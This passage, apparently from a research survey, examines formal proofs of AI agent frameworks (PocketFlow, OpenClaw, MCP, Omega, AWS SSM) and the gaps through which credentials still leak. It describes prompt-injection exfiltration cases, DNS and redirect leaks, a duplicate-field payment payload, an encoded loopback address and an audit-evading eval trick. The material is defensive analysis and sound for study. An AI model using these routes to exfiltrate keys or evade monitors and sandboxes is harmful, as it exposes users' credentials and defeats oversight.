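Several projects from 2025 and 2026 have applied formal tools to agent frameworks, platforms and protocols. Five of them cover access control, user approvals, sessions and attestation, but none proves that an agent's stored API keys reach only permitted destinations. The closest result, which concerns ordinary software rather than agents, shows with some gaps that a large management program from Amazon keeps its temporary encryption keys secret.

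### PocketFlow's control loop

PocketFlow is a small Python framework for building agents. A developer describes an agent as a graph. Each node does some work and outputs a label, and the framework follows the edge with that label to the next node. In *Containment Verification*, Moon and Varshney (2026) verify the loop that runs this graph. They believe theirs is the first proof of this kind for an agent framework.

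The language model is the attacker in this proof. Moon and Varshney use Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, and declare the call to the model as a method without any code. The declaration states only that the method returns an action, which must be one of four kinds. Dafny therefore has to check the loop for every action that a model could return. The policy has three rules:

- The agent reads only files inside a chosen workspace folder.
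- The agent calls only tools on an approved list.
- The agent takes no more than a fixed number of steps.

The proof compares two state machines. The abstract machine describes safe behaviour, and the concrete machine describes how the loop handles each action. Let R(m, i) mean that state m of the abstract machine corresponds to state i of the concrete one. Dafny checks these statements:

1. The abstract machine obeys the policy for every sequence of actions.
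2. The two starting states correspond.
3. If R(m, i) holds, and the concrete machine responds to action a with effect e and moves to i′, then the abstract machine can respond to a with a matching effect and move to a state m′ such that R(m′, i′) holds.
4. If the abstract step obeys the policy, so does the concrete step that it matches.

By induction, every run of the concrete machine has a matching abstract run with the same actions, so every concrete run obeys the policy. Suppose an injected instruction makes the model request a file outside the workspace that contains cloud passwords. The loop rejects the action, and the abstract machine matches this with a step that has no effect. If the programmer had forgotten to check the path, the loop would read the file. No safe abstract step would match that read, so the proof would fail.

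Dafny also checks executable code against the concrete machine and compiles this code to Python. The guarantee therefore applies to the compiled loop but not to the original PocketFlow code.

### What the PocketFlow proof leaves to trust

The trusted base includes the policy, the rules for matching states and effects, Dafny's verifier and compiler, and the code that turns the model's text into an action. The largest assumption is complete mediation, which Moon and Varshney call effect exclusivity. If a node's Python code opened a network connection directly, the request would bypass the loop. The formal model of the loop also omits timing, concurrency and hardware faults.

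The properties do not include credential secrecy. The policy would stop an agent from reading a key file outside the workspace, but not one inside it. If the approved list contains a tool that sends web requests, the policy allows the agent to send the key to any address, because it checks only which tool the agent calls. A stricter policy could restrict the destination, since the method allows rules about an action's arguments. That would still help little in a framework that lets the agent run arbitrary shell commands. Moon and Varshney note that the guarantee is then only as strong as that one action.

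A pipeline built on Claude models wrote specifications and proofs in Dafny for two example agents, and Dafny verified each path through the graph in 1.2 to 2.5 seconds. The danger is that a model may write a specification that is true of any program. To reduce this risk, the pipeline withholds the implementation from the step that writes the safety property, and it rejects a specification if deliberately damaged versions of the proof still pass.

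These precautions did not catch every error. In a comparison run, Moon and Varshney gave the property-writing step access to the implementation of a document-retrieval agent. The standard template had no field for that agent's main effects, and the resulting model left the nearest field empty. The safety rule about that field was therefore true in every state, and the file passed all the checks. With credentials, the same mistake could produce a theorem that every recorded transmission of a key goes to an allowed host, even though the model never records any such transmission.

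### A monitor for agents that attack websites

Some security firms use agents to look for weaknesses in a client's website by attacking it. Such an agent needs dangerous abilities, but only against that client. *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (David, Guarnieri and Gervais, 2026) defines a contract that limits what the agent may do and a monitor that enforces it. In the paper's main example, the agent may contact subdomains of example.com, use only the two web methods that fetch information, make at most 10,000 requests, and report only to the firm's dashboard.

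The monitor examines each event before it happens. An event is a network request, a file access or the start of a program. The monitor allows it only if all of the following are true:

- The target is in scope.
- The contract allows this type of action.
- The contract does not forbid this type of action.
- The total cost, including all earlier events, stays within the budget.
- Every disclosure that the event declares goes to a permitted recipient.

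Let P be any finite list of events that the agent proposes, and let Run(P) be the events that the monitor lets through. The main theorem, which Lean checks, is:

*For every P, Run(P) satisfies the contract.*

The proof is a short induction. An empty list satisfies the contract, and the monitor adds an event only after checking it. The proof doesn't depend on the agent's motives. If a web page contains instructions to send the agent's findings to evil.com, the monitor blocks the transfer because evil.com is out of scope.

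Lean also checks two theorems for combining contracts. A run that satisfies a stricter contract also satisfies a looser one. A run that satisfies the combination of two contracts satisfies each of them, if both contracts measure costs and declare disclosures in the same way. A firm could therefore combine its own rules with a client's.

The main theorem is easy to prove because the monitor applies the contract's own definition to each event. Connecting events to a running system is harder. David and colleagues assume that every relevant effect produces a correct event, that the event reaches the monitor in time to block the effect, and that the event declares every disclosure that matters. Lean does not check these assumptions, and the paper does not implement the monitor.

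The last assumption is the main difficulty for credentials. The paper lists credentials among the outputs that should reach only authorized channels, but the monitor doesn't inspect the contents of messages. In the example, the event for a web request records the destination, port, protocol, method and size, but not the URL path or the body. The monitor therefore can't distinguish a request with a key in its path from one with harmless text of the same length. If the agent is testing a hostile server, which the threat model permits, it can send that server the key while staying within the contract's scope.

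To prevent this, the software that creates the events would have to recognize that the request contains a key and declare the disclosure. Labels like those in FIDES could identify the key, but the labelling software would then become part of the trusted base.

### OpenClaw's models and their faulty versions

OpenClaw is the personal assistant whose control page leaked gateway tokens. OpenClaw's *Formal verification (security models)* lists eight groups of claims, with models in TLA+ for the model checker TLC. They include the following:

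- If the gateway accepts connections from other machines, a token or password blocks attackers who haven't authenticated.
- A command runs on a connected device only if it is on the list of allowed commands and, where the owner requires approval, someone has approved it. Nobody can reuse an old approval.
- In a group chat where users must mention the assistant by name, an unauthorized command cannot bypass this requirement.
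- Direct messages from different people stay in separate sessions unless the owner has linked or configured them otherwise.

The documentation calls the last property "session-key isolation", but these keys identify conversations and are unrelated to encryption. By default, all of a single owner's direct messages share one session. Separate sessions require a different setting, which the project expects assistants with several users to use.

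Many of the claims come with a deliberately faulty model. The page lists 18 checks that should pass and 17 that should fail. One example concerns pairing requests, which new contacts send to ask permission to message the assistant. Suppose at most three requests may wait at once, two are already waiting, and two more arrive together. In the faulty model, the software counts the waiting requests in one step and adds the new one in another. It can therefore count two waiting requests for both new arrivals before adding either, which leaves four waiting. TLC should report this sequence. In the correct model, counting and adding form a single step, so TLC should find no violation.

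The faulty models test whether the claims are strong enough to detect realistic mistakes. If TLC accepted the faulty pairing model, passing the same check would be no evidence for the correct one. The damaged proofs in the PocketFlow pipeline guard against the same problem.

OpenClaw states several limits. The models do not verify the TypeScript program, which can change while the models stay the same. TLC examines only a finite number of states, and some claims assume that the owner has deployed and configured the software correctly. The project also doesn't run the checks automatically when the program changes. Outsiders cannot currently repeat the checks or confirm the results, because the repository that held the models is not publicly reachable. The documentation still shows what the project set out to check.

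None of the listed claims concerns credentials leaving the system. The gateway claim is that a token keeps out attackers who have not authenticated. In the attack that used the control page flaw, the victim's browser gave the token to the attacker, who then authenticated normally, so the attack can succeed even if the gateway claim is true.

### Session hijacking in the Model Context Protocol

A server that uses the Model Context Protocol can give each session an identifier to group related requests. An attacker who has someone else's identifier may be able to add messages to that session's queue or send requests as the victim. *Confidence-Guided Protocol IR for LLM-Aided Security Protocol Modeling* (Li, Cai and colleagues, 2026) models both attacks in Tamarin.

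The important lemma concerns authorization. Simplified, it is:

*For every run: if the server accepts request r at step j, then someone authorized to use the session sent r at some step i < j.*

Tamarin found a counterexample. The modelled server accepts a request if its identifier matches the stored one, without checking who sent it. The identifier therefore works as a bearer credential, although its purpose is only to sort requests into sessions. The server needs a separate check that the sender is allowed to use the session.

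Tamarin's "verified" label can mislead, because it also applies to two lemmas stating that the attacks are possible.

The model follows a published description of the attacks, so Tamarin reproduced them and did not discover new ones. The model also doesn't represent any particular server's code, and a server that already checks the sender would not have this flaw. The reported lemmas concern only what happens once a request arrives with a valid identifier, and none of them covers credential secrecy.

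A language model drafted the description of the protocol from ordinary text, a person reviewed the draft, and software turned it into a Tamarin model. Li and colleagues tested this process on 18 known protocols. When GPT-5.5 wrote the drafts, Tamarin accepted all 18 models, and 14 produced the expected results. However, the generated Tamarin models agreed least with human-written ones on the checks that a participant makes before trusting a message, with an average score of 0.48 out of 1.

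One generated model, of the key-exchange protocol EDHOC, had a single process create both sides' messages and then verify its own signature. The process received nothing from the network in between, so the attacker could not interfere at that point. Tamarin still gave the expected results, so a proof from a generated model needs careful review. The counterexample for the Model Context Protocol is easier to trust because a reader can compare its steps with a server's behaviour.

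### Omega's attestation protocol

A server that checks its senders may still be running altered software. *Trusted AI Agents in the Cloud* (Bodea, Misono and colleagues, 2025) addresses this problem with Omega, a system for running agents on rented machines without trusting the company that owns them. Omega is designed to withstand an attacker who controls the host's operating system, network and storage. It runs agents inside a confidential virtual machine, whose memory the processor protects from the host, and runs the language model on a graphics processor with similar protection.

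Before sending a credential or other private data to Omega, the user needs evidence that the genuine software will receive it. The attestation protocol provides this evidence:

1. As the machine starts, it records a hash of each component that it loads.
2. The user sends Omega a nonce.
3. Omega creates a public and private key and obtains a report from the processor. The report covers the nonce, a hash of the public key, and a hash of the graphics processor's own report.
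4. The user checks the reports and completes a key exchange with Omega. The resulting shared key encrypts the user's requests.
5. After each task, Omega returns a shorter report that covers the user's input, policy and result, together with the stored hashes of the agent's policy, the language model and its data.

The nonce prevents the cloud company from replaying an old report. The hash of the public key prevents the company from attaching a genuine report to its own key, which would let it decrypt the user's requests. The short reports save time because Omega doesn't have to measure the whole system again for every task.

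The Tamarin analysis of Omega covers its attestation protocol. Such an analysis can show that a user's encrypted request is tied to known software, but not what the software does with a credential afterwards. Bodea and colleagues assume that a component behaves as expected once its hash has passed the check. An agent whose code leaks credentials would still produce a correct hash, because the hash only identifies the code.

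A separate policy engine controls what agents send out by checking each tool call and each message to another agent against rules, such as one that limits an agent to a market data tool. The evidence for this engine comes from tests on a benchmark of attacks on the Model Context Protocol. The threat model excludes physical attacks and side channels.

### Secrecy in a large Go program

Secrecy is difficult to verify in code partly because a leak can occur anywhere. A logging statement in an unrelated part of a program can print a key, so earlier methods, including the C verification by Dupressoir and colleagues, required engineers to verify the entire program. *The Secrets Must Not Flow* (Arquint, Kishor and colleagues, 2025) presents a method that limits the detailed proof to a small part of the program.

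Researchers applied a method called Diodon to the AWS Systems Manager Agent, which Amazon's cloud customers use to configure and manage their virtual machines. It is not an AI agent. It has more than 100,000 lines of Go code. One part lets a customer open an encrypted command-line session on a remote machine, and the secrets are the two keys that encrypt this session.

The researchers divided the program into a Core and an Application. The Core is the package that implements the session protocol. It has 750 lines, or about 1% of the program. The Application is everything else. The argument has four parts:

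1. Tamarin proves that an attacker who controls the network does not learn the session keys, unless he has obtained a participant's signing key or the key of a trusted monitor that may inspect sessions. It also proves injective agreement on the keys and identities.
2. Gobra, a verifier for Go, proves that the Core sends only the protocol messages that the Tamarin model permits. Tamarin generates a set of permissions from the model, and each network operation uses one up.
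3. Argot, a program that analyses Go code automatically, follows the secrets through the entire program. It checks that they do not influence any output outside the protocol, such as writing to a file, sending data or starting another program.
4. Argot also checks that the Application uses the Core in the way that Gobra's proof assumes. For example, the Application must not change the Core's internal data.

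The third part works because the attacker could himself have produced any output that doesn't depend on a secret, and the Tamarin model already includes an attacker who can do so. The engineers therefore don't have to describe the Application's thousands of ordinary operations in the protocol model.

| Part of the argument | Tool | Person-months | Running time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Protocol model | Tamarin | Less than 2 | 3.2 minutes |
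| Proof of the Core | Gobra | Less than 3 | 1.3 minutes |
| Search for leaks in the whole program | Argot | Less than 0.5 | 0.6 minutes |
| Checks on how the Application uses the Core | Argot | Less than 1.5 | 2.5 minutes |

The work took less than seven person-months in total. The Core needed 3,825 lines of specifications and proof annotations, of which Tamarin generated 1,064. That is about five lines per line of code, almost the same ratio as in the Quark browser kernel.

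Arquint and colleagues found two errors before release. In an early version of the protocol, the signatures did not include the intended recipient's identity, so an attacker could get between the two sides. A missing name had also made Lowe's attack possible. The second error was a data race, in which two threads could use the same data without proper coordination. They also planted leaks to test the tools. Argot reported a line that logged the Core's internal state, and Gobra rejected a version that sent a secret key unencrypted.

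### Gaps in the proof about Amazon's program

The proof for the 100,000 lines is incomplete. It requires that functions in the Application never call back into the Core while the Core is calling them, but checking this still needs a more precise tool. Some of Argot's other checks raised false alarms, and the researchers inspected at least one of these by hand. They also assumed that the Application has no data races and that an older protocol in the same package is switched off. The secrecy theorem for the whole protocol requires every participant's software to follow the model, but the researchers verified only one side.

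Information can also leak through branches, as in the program that copies a key one character at a time. Argot normally prevents this by rejecting any branch that depends on a secret. The researchers made exceptions for false alarms and for some harmless cases, such as testing whether a message decrypts correctly, and each exception depends on a person's judgment.

The search for leaks starts only from the secret values that the program generates for the key exchange, so it doesn't follow other credentials the program may hold. An engineer who wanted to protect stored API keys would have to mark them as secrets too.

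The same division could suit an AI agent that uses a broker. The broker would be the Core, with a protocol model that permits it to send each key only to the right service, and the rest of the runtime would be the Application. The analysis would report any path by which a key could enter a prompt, because the runtime normally sends prompts to the model over a network. However, it could examine only code that exists when it runs, so scripts that the model writes later would have to be isolated from the keys.

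### Comparison of the cases

The table also includes SUDP, the broker protocol with user approvals, and PlanTERS, the framework for agents with fixed plans.

| Case | What the proof or check covers | Tool | Attacker | Credential secrecy among the properties? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| PocketFlow | Code for the control loop, written in Dafny | Dafny | A language model that may choose any action | No |
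| Alignment Contracts | A model of a monitor | Lean | An agent that may propose any action | Only for disclosures that an event declares |
| OpenClaw | Models of access, approvals and sessions, with a finite number of states | TLC | Outsiders and unauthorized users | No |
| Model Context Protocol sessions | A model of a known attack | Tamarin | Someone with another user's session identifier | No; the main lemma concerns authorization |
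| Omega | A model of the attestation protocol | Tamarin | The cloud company | No control over where agents send credentials |
| AWS Systems Manager Agent | A protocol model, 750 lines of code, and an automatic analysis of the whole program | Tamarin, Gobra and Argot | Someone who controls the network | Yes, for session keys |
| SUDP | A model of the protocol | Proof by hand | A compromised agent and network | Yes, apart from what results reveal |
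| PlanTERS | A model of agents with fixed plans | Isabelle | Someone who supplies content with injected instructions | Only that injections add no new leaks |

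## How can a proved system still leak a key?

A correct secrecy proof applies to a running system only if the system meets the proof's assumptions. An attacker can look for a network route, service or piece of code that the model omits or describes wrongly. Several agent systems have had such gaps.

### Routes around the broker

Secrecy proofs for brokers assume complete mediation. This assumption fails if the agent can run shell commands, install plugins or open a network connection that the broker doesn't check.

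*Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026) tested how well four agents meet this assumption. The agents were OpenClaw; IronClaw, a security-focused rewrite; Nanobot, a deliberately small agent; and NemoClaw, Nvidia's sandbox for OpenClaw. The researchers treated the language model as an operating system treats an untrusted user, so the surrounding software had to enforce every limit. They ran each agent in a virtual machine with the recommended settings and restored the machine to the same clean state before every attack. A monitor in the operating system checked whether the attack reached its goal within three attempts.

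| Attack | OpenClaw | IronClaw | Nanobot | NemoClaw |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read secrets in environment variables | Succeeded | Failed | Failed | Failed |
| Collect stored credentials | Succeeded | Failed | Failed | Failed |
| Fetch any web address | Succeeded | Succeeded | Succeeded | Failed |
| Message an unauthorized recipient | Succeeded | Succeeded | Succeeded | Succeeded |
| Read another user's session | Succeeded | Succeeded | Succeeded | Succeeded |
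| Successes among all applicable attacks | 16 of 16 | 7 of 12 | 7 of 15 | 11 of 16 |

NemoClaw blocked web requests to arbitrary addresses, but an attacker could still make it message strangers through its chat account. Those messages could include a key that a user had pasted into a conversation. Configuration files can also cause an agent to leak a key. Donenfeld and Vanunu (2026) report in *Caught in the Hook* that opening an untrusted project in Claude Code could run an attacker's commands and send out the user's Anthropic API key.

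The usual remedy is a sandbox whose only network connection leads to the broker. But a filter on network addresses can identify only the connection to the chat service, not the recipient of each message, so every permitted channel needs its own rules. A malicious skill may also replace a trusted tool with another program of the same name. Pirch and colleagues found that NemoClaw still allowed this, and they warn that an agent could resist all their attacks and still be insecure.

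### Allowed hosts where the attacker has an account

Claude Cowork, an agent made by Anthropic, by default allows web traffic only to a list of approved domains. *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, 2026) describes how the company Prompt Armor got around this restriction. Anthropic's own API was on the list, so the injected instructions supplied the attacker's API key and told the agent to upload the user's files to the attacker's Anthropic account. A credential stored in one of those files would have leaked too. SecurityWeek describes a similar attack on Claude by the researcher Johann Rehberger.

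Every request in this attack goes to an allowed host, so a theorem about host names remains true. The theorem would also have to cover the account each request uses. A broker can ensure that requests use the user's account by removing any credential the agent supplies and inserting the user's own, as CapSeal does for web requests. To do this, the broker has to read the request inside the encrypted connection, which a filter on domain names can't do.

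This remedy doesn't help if the user's own account can pass data to strangers. Many services let users publish comments or share folders, so the broker also needs rules for individual operations.

### Keys in replies and redirects

The proof for the four-rule broker relies on the assumption that the service never returns the key. A real service might break this assumption by quoting a rejected request, including the key, in an error message. Searching responses for the key can miss encoded copies, so it is safer for the broker to pass on only named fields that the agent needs, such as the number and title of a bug report.

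In *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary*, Millstone, Akidau and colleagues (2026) tested a proxy that filters replies in this way. They work for Redpanda, a data company that uses a fuller version of the design. Their 3,621 trials used simulated copies of Jira and ServiceNow, two services for tracking work. A trial counted as a failure if protected data reached the agent or appeared verbatim in its answer, or if a forbidden change went through. In the main comparison, the proxy reduced the failure rate from 57.6% to 0.2%, but the share of requests the agents fulfilled also fell, from 79.1% to 60.9%.

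Some information still got past the filter. Four answers contained an exact protected value that the agent had never received but had reconstructed. In another trial, the agent learned something from the number of rows left after filtering. A random 32-byte key is much harder to reconstruct than ordinary business data. But if an agent can search records that contain the key, row counts could reveal it just as the byte-guessing tool's answers do.

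Redirects have caused repeated leaks in OpenClaw. OSV's *GHSA-6mgf-v5j7-45cr* (March 2026) describes a function that removed four named headers before following a redirect to another site. It left others, including `X-Api-Key`, so a service that could trigger a redirect could get the key. The developers replaced the list of headers to remove with a list of harmless headers to keep.

The same kind of flaw then appeared elsewhere in the program. OSV's *GHSA-68v4-hmwv-f43h* (April 2026) describes it in media downloads, in a version released after that repair, and OSV's *CVE-2026-53840* (June 2026) describes it in connections to Model Context Protocol servers. Developers can avoid repeating the flaw by sending all web requests through one function, but they then have to ensure that no code bypasses it. A list of safe headers doesn't protect a key in the web address or body of a request. Refusing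 all redirects would be safer but would break services that depend on them.

### Two readings of one request

Suppose an agent sends a payment request that contains the amount twice:

`{"amount": 20, "amount": 2000}`

When a message repeats a field, some programs keep the first value and others keep the last. If the broker reads 20 and the bank reads 2,000, the bank makes a payment that nobody approved. The same problem can affect destinations. The number 2130706433 is another way to write 127.0.0.1, the address a computer uses to reach itself, so a check that looks only for the familiar form can miss it. Symbolic proofs usually exclude such attacks implicitly, because a message in the model is a single expression that everyone reads the same way.

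Pirch and colleagues found a mismatch of this kind in OpenClaw's security audit. The audit searches for `eval`, a JavaScript function that runs text as code, but it detects a call only if the parentheses are on the same line as `eval`. JavaScript also allows them on a later line, so a malicious skill can pass the audit and still run its code.

The broker can avoid many mismatches by extracting the fields it can parse, discarding the original text and writing a new request from those fields. The bank would then receive only one amount. Millstone and colleagues use a connector to translate requests into typed fields, and they require the proxy to deny or separately control anything the connector doesn't cover. But someone has to write a connector for each service and update it when the service changes. If the connector parses a field incorrectly, the broker will work as proved but enforce the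 wrong policy. SUDP's adapters must be written and maintained with the same care.

### DNS, message length, crash files and timing

Before a program connects to a host, it usually asks the domain name system (DNS) for the host's numerical address. The query contains the host's name and can reach a server run by the domain's owner, so the name can carry data to that owner even if a firewall blocks the connection that follows. Embrace The Red's *Claude Code* documents such a leak in that agent (CVE-2025-55284). A sandbox can prevent this by looking up only approved names, but a rule that approves every name under a domain still lets the agent choose part of each name.

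Encryption hides the contents of a message but not its length. If a broker compresses a request before encrypting it, text chosen by the attacker may be compressed together with the key. Repeated text compresses better, so the message may be shorter when the attacker's text matches part of the key. The broker can avoid this by not compressing requests that contain credentials. It can also pad messages to a fixed length, but this uses more bandwidth and doesn't hide how many messages it sends or when.

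An operating system may save a crashed program's memory to a file, including any keys the program was using. Some programs then upload the file to their developer. An administrator can turn this off for the broker, but faults are then harder to diagnose.

Timing leaks are harder to eliminate. Bhargavan (2026) warns in *The strengths and limits of formal verification* that compilers can turn constant-time code into code that branches on secrets. He works at Cryspen, which develops the partly verified cryptographic library libcrux, and says the company doesn't prove that the compiled library resists side-channel attacks.

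*An AI Approach to Verified Production Cryptographic Libraries* (2026) reports that an AI system produced proofs for the widely used library curve25519-dalek in 11.4 hours. The proofs show that the functions compute the right results, but not that they run in constant time. Engineers can check for constant time by analysing the compiled program, but they have to repeat the analysis when they recompile it, and the result still depends on how the processor behaves.

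### Hardware protection for keys in memory

Confidential computing protects a program's memory with trusted execution environments, the hardware SUDP relies on. Intel's SGX protects part of a program from the rest of the machine, including its operating system. Intel's TDX and AMD's SEV-SNP protect a whole virtual machine from the company that hosts it.

How well a hardware-protected environment protects credentials depends on what else is inside it. One illustrative design in *When Agents Handle Secrets* (Forough, Kogias and Haddadi, 2026) puts the agent, its credentials and the policy checks in a single protected environment. The cloud company can't read the credentials directly, but the hardware doesn't separate them from the agent. The paper also notes that such hardware can't stop a prompt-injected agent from leaking data through its own tool calls. A credential broker therefore needs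 its own protected environment, with the agent outside.

An attacker may still learn the key indirectly. In some designs, the operating system still manages the protected program's memory in blocks called pages, and can see which page the program uses next. If the program uses one page when a bit of the key is 0 and another when it is 1, the operating system can work out the key without reading it. Forough and colleagues list several other side channels, including timing, shared caches and data left behind in graphics processors. Of the seven systems in their main comparison, three partly address side channels and four don't address them.

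A cloud company might also restart a protected machine from an old copy of its storage. A broker that keeps its list of used approvals there could then accept the same approval twice. To prevent this, the broker needs a record that the company can't reset.

Hardware isolation is still a substantial improvement against a dishonest host. It replaces the assumption that nobody can read the broker's memory with two narrower ones: that the processor works as specified, and that the broker's timing and memory use don't reveal the key.

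### Servers that depart from the specification

A protocol proof applies to a server only if the server follows the protocol. In *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*, Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026) used two search engines for internet-connected machines to identify 7,973 live Model Context Protocol servers. Of these, 3,233 (40.55%) offered tools without authentication, 2,312 used fixed tokens or API keys, and 2,428 used OAuth. Most of the open servers they sampled appeared to be tests or demonstrations, but one let anyone query more than 5,000 internal records, including customers' names and addresses.

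The researchers then tested the OAuth servers for nine flaws. In a normal OAuth exchange, the user approves access in a browser, and the server sends a short-lived code to the client program's return address. The client then swaps the code for an access token. PKCE, an added protection, requires the client to prove with a one-time secret that it started the exchange.

The tests needed servers that let new clients register automatically, which 1,118 of the 2,428 did. After the team removed duplicates and servers that they couldn't test, 119 remained. Every one had at least one flaw:

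| Flaw | Servers affected, out of 119 |
|---|---|
| Anyone can register a client with any return address | 114 |
| The server accepts requests without PKCE, or with a weak form of it | 81 |
| The approval page doesn't show where the code will go | 72 |
| The server doesn't properly check the return address against the registered one | 28 |
| The server accepts clients that never registered | 12 |
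| The server requires PKCE from the client but omits it when contacting another service | 12 |
| An attacker can change a return address stored inside another value | 7 |
| A code works more than once | 6 |
| The value that ties the reply to the user's session is missing or predictable | 3 |

Zhou and colleagues report 325 flaws in total, although the individual counts add up to 335. The study led to nine entries in the public CVE list of vulnerabilities.

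The most common flaw lets an attacker register his own return address and send the user a link to the server's real approval page. If the user approves, the server sends a code to the attacker, who exchanges it for a token. A proof about the user's broker doesn't cover this attack because the stolen token never passes through the broker.

These rates don't describe all servers for the protocol. The team chose servers with automatic registration, so the count of 114 can't be extended to the 1,310 OAuth servers that lack it. They also excluded 316 servers with strict company access controls, which may have been better protected than the rest.

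The first version of the specification, from November 2024, didn't require authentication for remote servers. The March 2025 version made OAuth mandatory for authentication over the web, and two more revisions followed that year. Clients can test a server before trusting it, but the operator may change the server afterwards.

Verified code can similarly change so that its proof no longer applies. According to Bhargavan, Cryspen reruns its proofs for every proposed change and accepts the change only if they pass. This works because the proofs are about the code itself and not about a separate model like OpenClaw's. Translating the code for verification can also introduce errors. *Verification Facade* (Kobeissi, 2026) describes three kinds of gap between programs written in Rust and the versions that Cryspen's tool hax produces for verification.

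### True but empty theorems

A broker that refuses every request never leaks a key. It satisfies trace secrecy and noninterference, provided its refusals don't depend on the key. It also satisfies the authorization theorem vacuously, because it never executes an action.

A small mistake in a model can produce this broker. Suppose the agent's rule sends messages tagged "request", but the broker's rule accepts only messages tagged "Request". The broker's rule never applies, so the modeled broker never makes a call that could leak the key. A tool will correctly report that the key stays secret in the model, even if the real broker sends it to anyone who asks.

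An executability lemma, like Paulson's check that each protocol can finish, detects this mistake by requiring at least one successful run:

*There is a run in which the agent requests b, the broker sends (s, b) to D, and D accepts the request.*

The model with mismatched tags has no such run, so the lemma fails.

Li and colleagues used Tamarin to model GitHub Actions, a service that builds and deploys software automatically. They compared three policies for choosing which file to deploy. If the policy checks only the file's name, an attacker can substitute a file from another build run. Requiring the file to come from the run that triggered the deployment prevents this, but that run may have started from a stranger's copy of the project. The strictest policy also checks the project and branch. Tamarin found no attack on it, and an executability lemma showed that legitimate deployments were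 still possible.

The two weaker policies served a similar purpose to the deliberately faulty models for OpenClaw. Tamarin found the expected attacks on these policies, which showed that the lemmas could detect those attacks. Neither the executability lemma above nor the use of faulty models is a complete safeguard. A broker that accepts one harmless request and refuses everything else satisfies the lemma, and faulty models test only for mistakes the engineer has thought of.

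A theorem can also describe real behaviour but leave out most of it. *Pre-QED* (2026) discusses OSS-Verify, a method that takes its specification from an existing test program. The resulting proof covers only the calls the test program makes, with inputs smaller than 64 MB. If a broker's test program never triggered a redirect, the proof would not cover redirects.

In other cases, the specification is wrong. *Function Contracts and Beyond* (2026) examines proofs that an AI coding agent wrote about a library for the hash function SHA-256. All six proof files passed a fresh check, but a counterexample involving an error case showed that the theorems couldn't support a conclusion about the real library. A model can also misrepresent the attacker. Li and colleagues found that one generated model matched the human-written version message for message but omitted repeated sessions and stolen long-term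 keys.

### Do these gaps make proofs worthless?

An attacker needs only one gap, and people who hear that a system is "verified" may stop looking for gaps. *Verification Theatre* (Kobeissi, 2026) supports this concern with thirteen vulnerabilities that escaped formal verification in libcrux and a related library, hpke-rs. Nine were in unverified code, including a bug that caused decryption failures in the messaging service Signal. The other four were in the verified specifications and proofs, including a wrong constant and a false proof.

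Bhargavan replies that verification can remove whole classes of bugs from large parts of a program, so testers can concentrate on the rest. His main example is HACL*, an older library with about 135,000 lines of C and assembly generated from verified source, plus 1,800 lines of supporting C code. By his account, most of the bugs users found in nine years were in the supporting code, and the developers twice had to correct a specification.

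He also wrote in February 2026 that nobody had found a bug in libcrux's verified code. Symbolic Software's *We Found Bugs in CE Labs' Verified Code* (2026) disputes this. Kobeissi works for Symbolic Software, so both sides have an interest in the outcome. Both agree that developers should state exactly what a proof covers and rerun it whenever the code changes.

Kobeissi's count is good evidence against trusting the word "verified" without knowing its scope. It doesn't show that verification failed to prevent other bugs, because a list of bugs that escaped can't measure how many the proofs caught. For a credential broker, a proof also turns a vague question about safety into conditions that engineers can test separately:

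| Condition | A test that could show it is false |
|---|---|
| The agent can reach the network only through the broker | Try to contact a test machine by web, DNS, email, chat and shell |
| Requests to an allowed host use only the user's account | Try to upload a file with the key of a second account |
| Replies and saved files don't contain the key | Use a marked test key and search for it, including encoded forms |
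| Redirects don't carry the key to another host | Redirect every part of the program that makes web requests |
| The broker and the service read requests alike | Send ambiguous requests and compare what each of them does |
| The proof covers the current software and can detect a leak | Rerun it after each change, and check that a deliberately leaky version fails |

Passing these tests doesn't prove that the conditions always hold. But most of the conditions concern ordinary software with a limited number of routes and settings, which engineers can inspect directly, unlike a language model's response to malicious text.

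The service's behaviour is the hardest condition to establish, because the broker's operator usually can't inspect the service's code and the service may change at any time. Signing keys largely avoid this problem, because the service never receives the private key.
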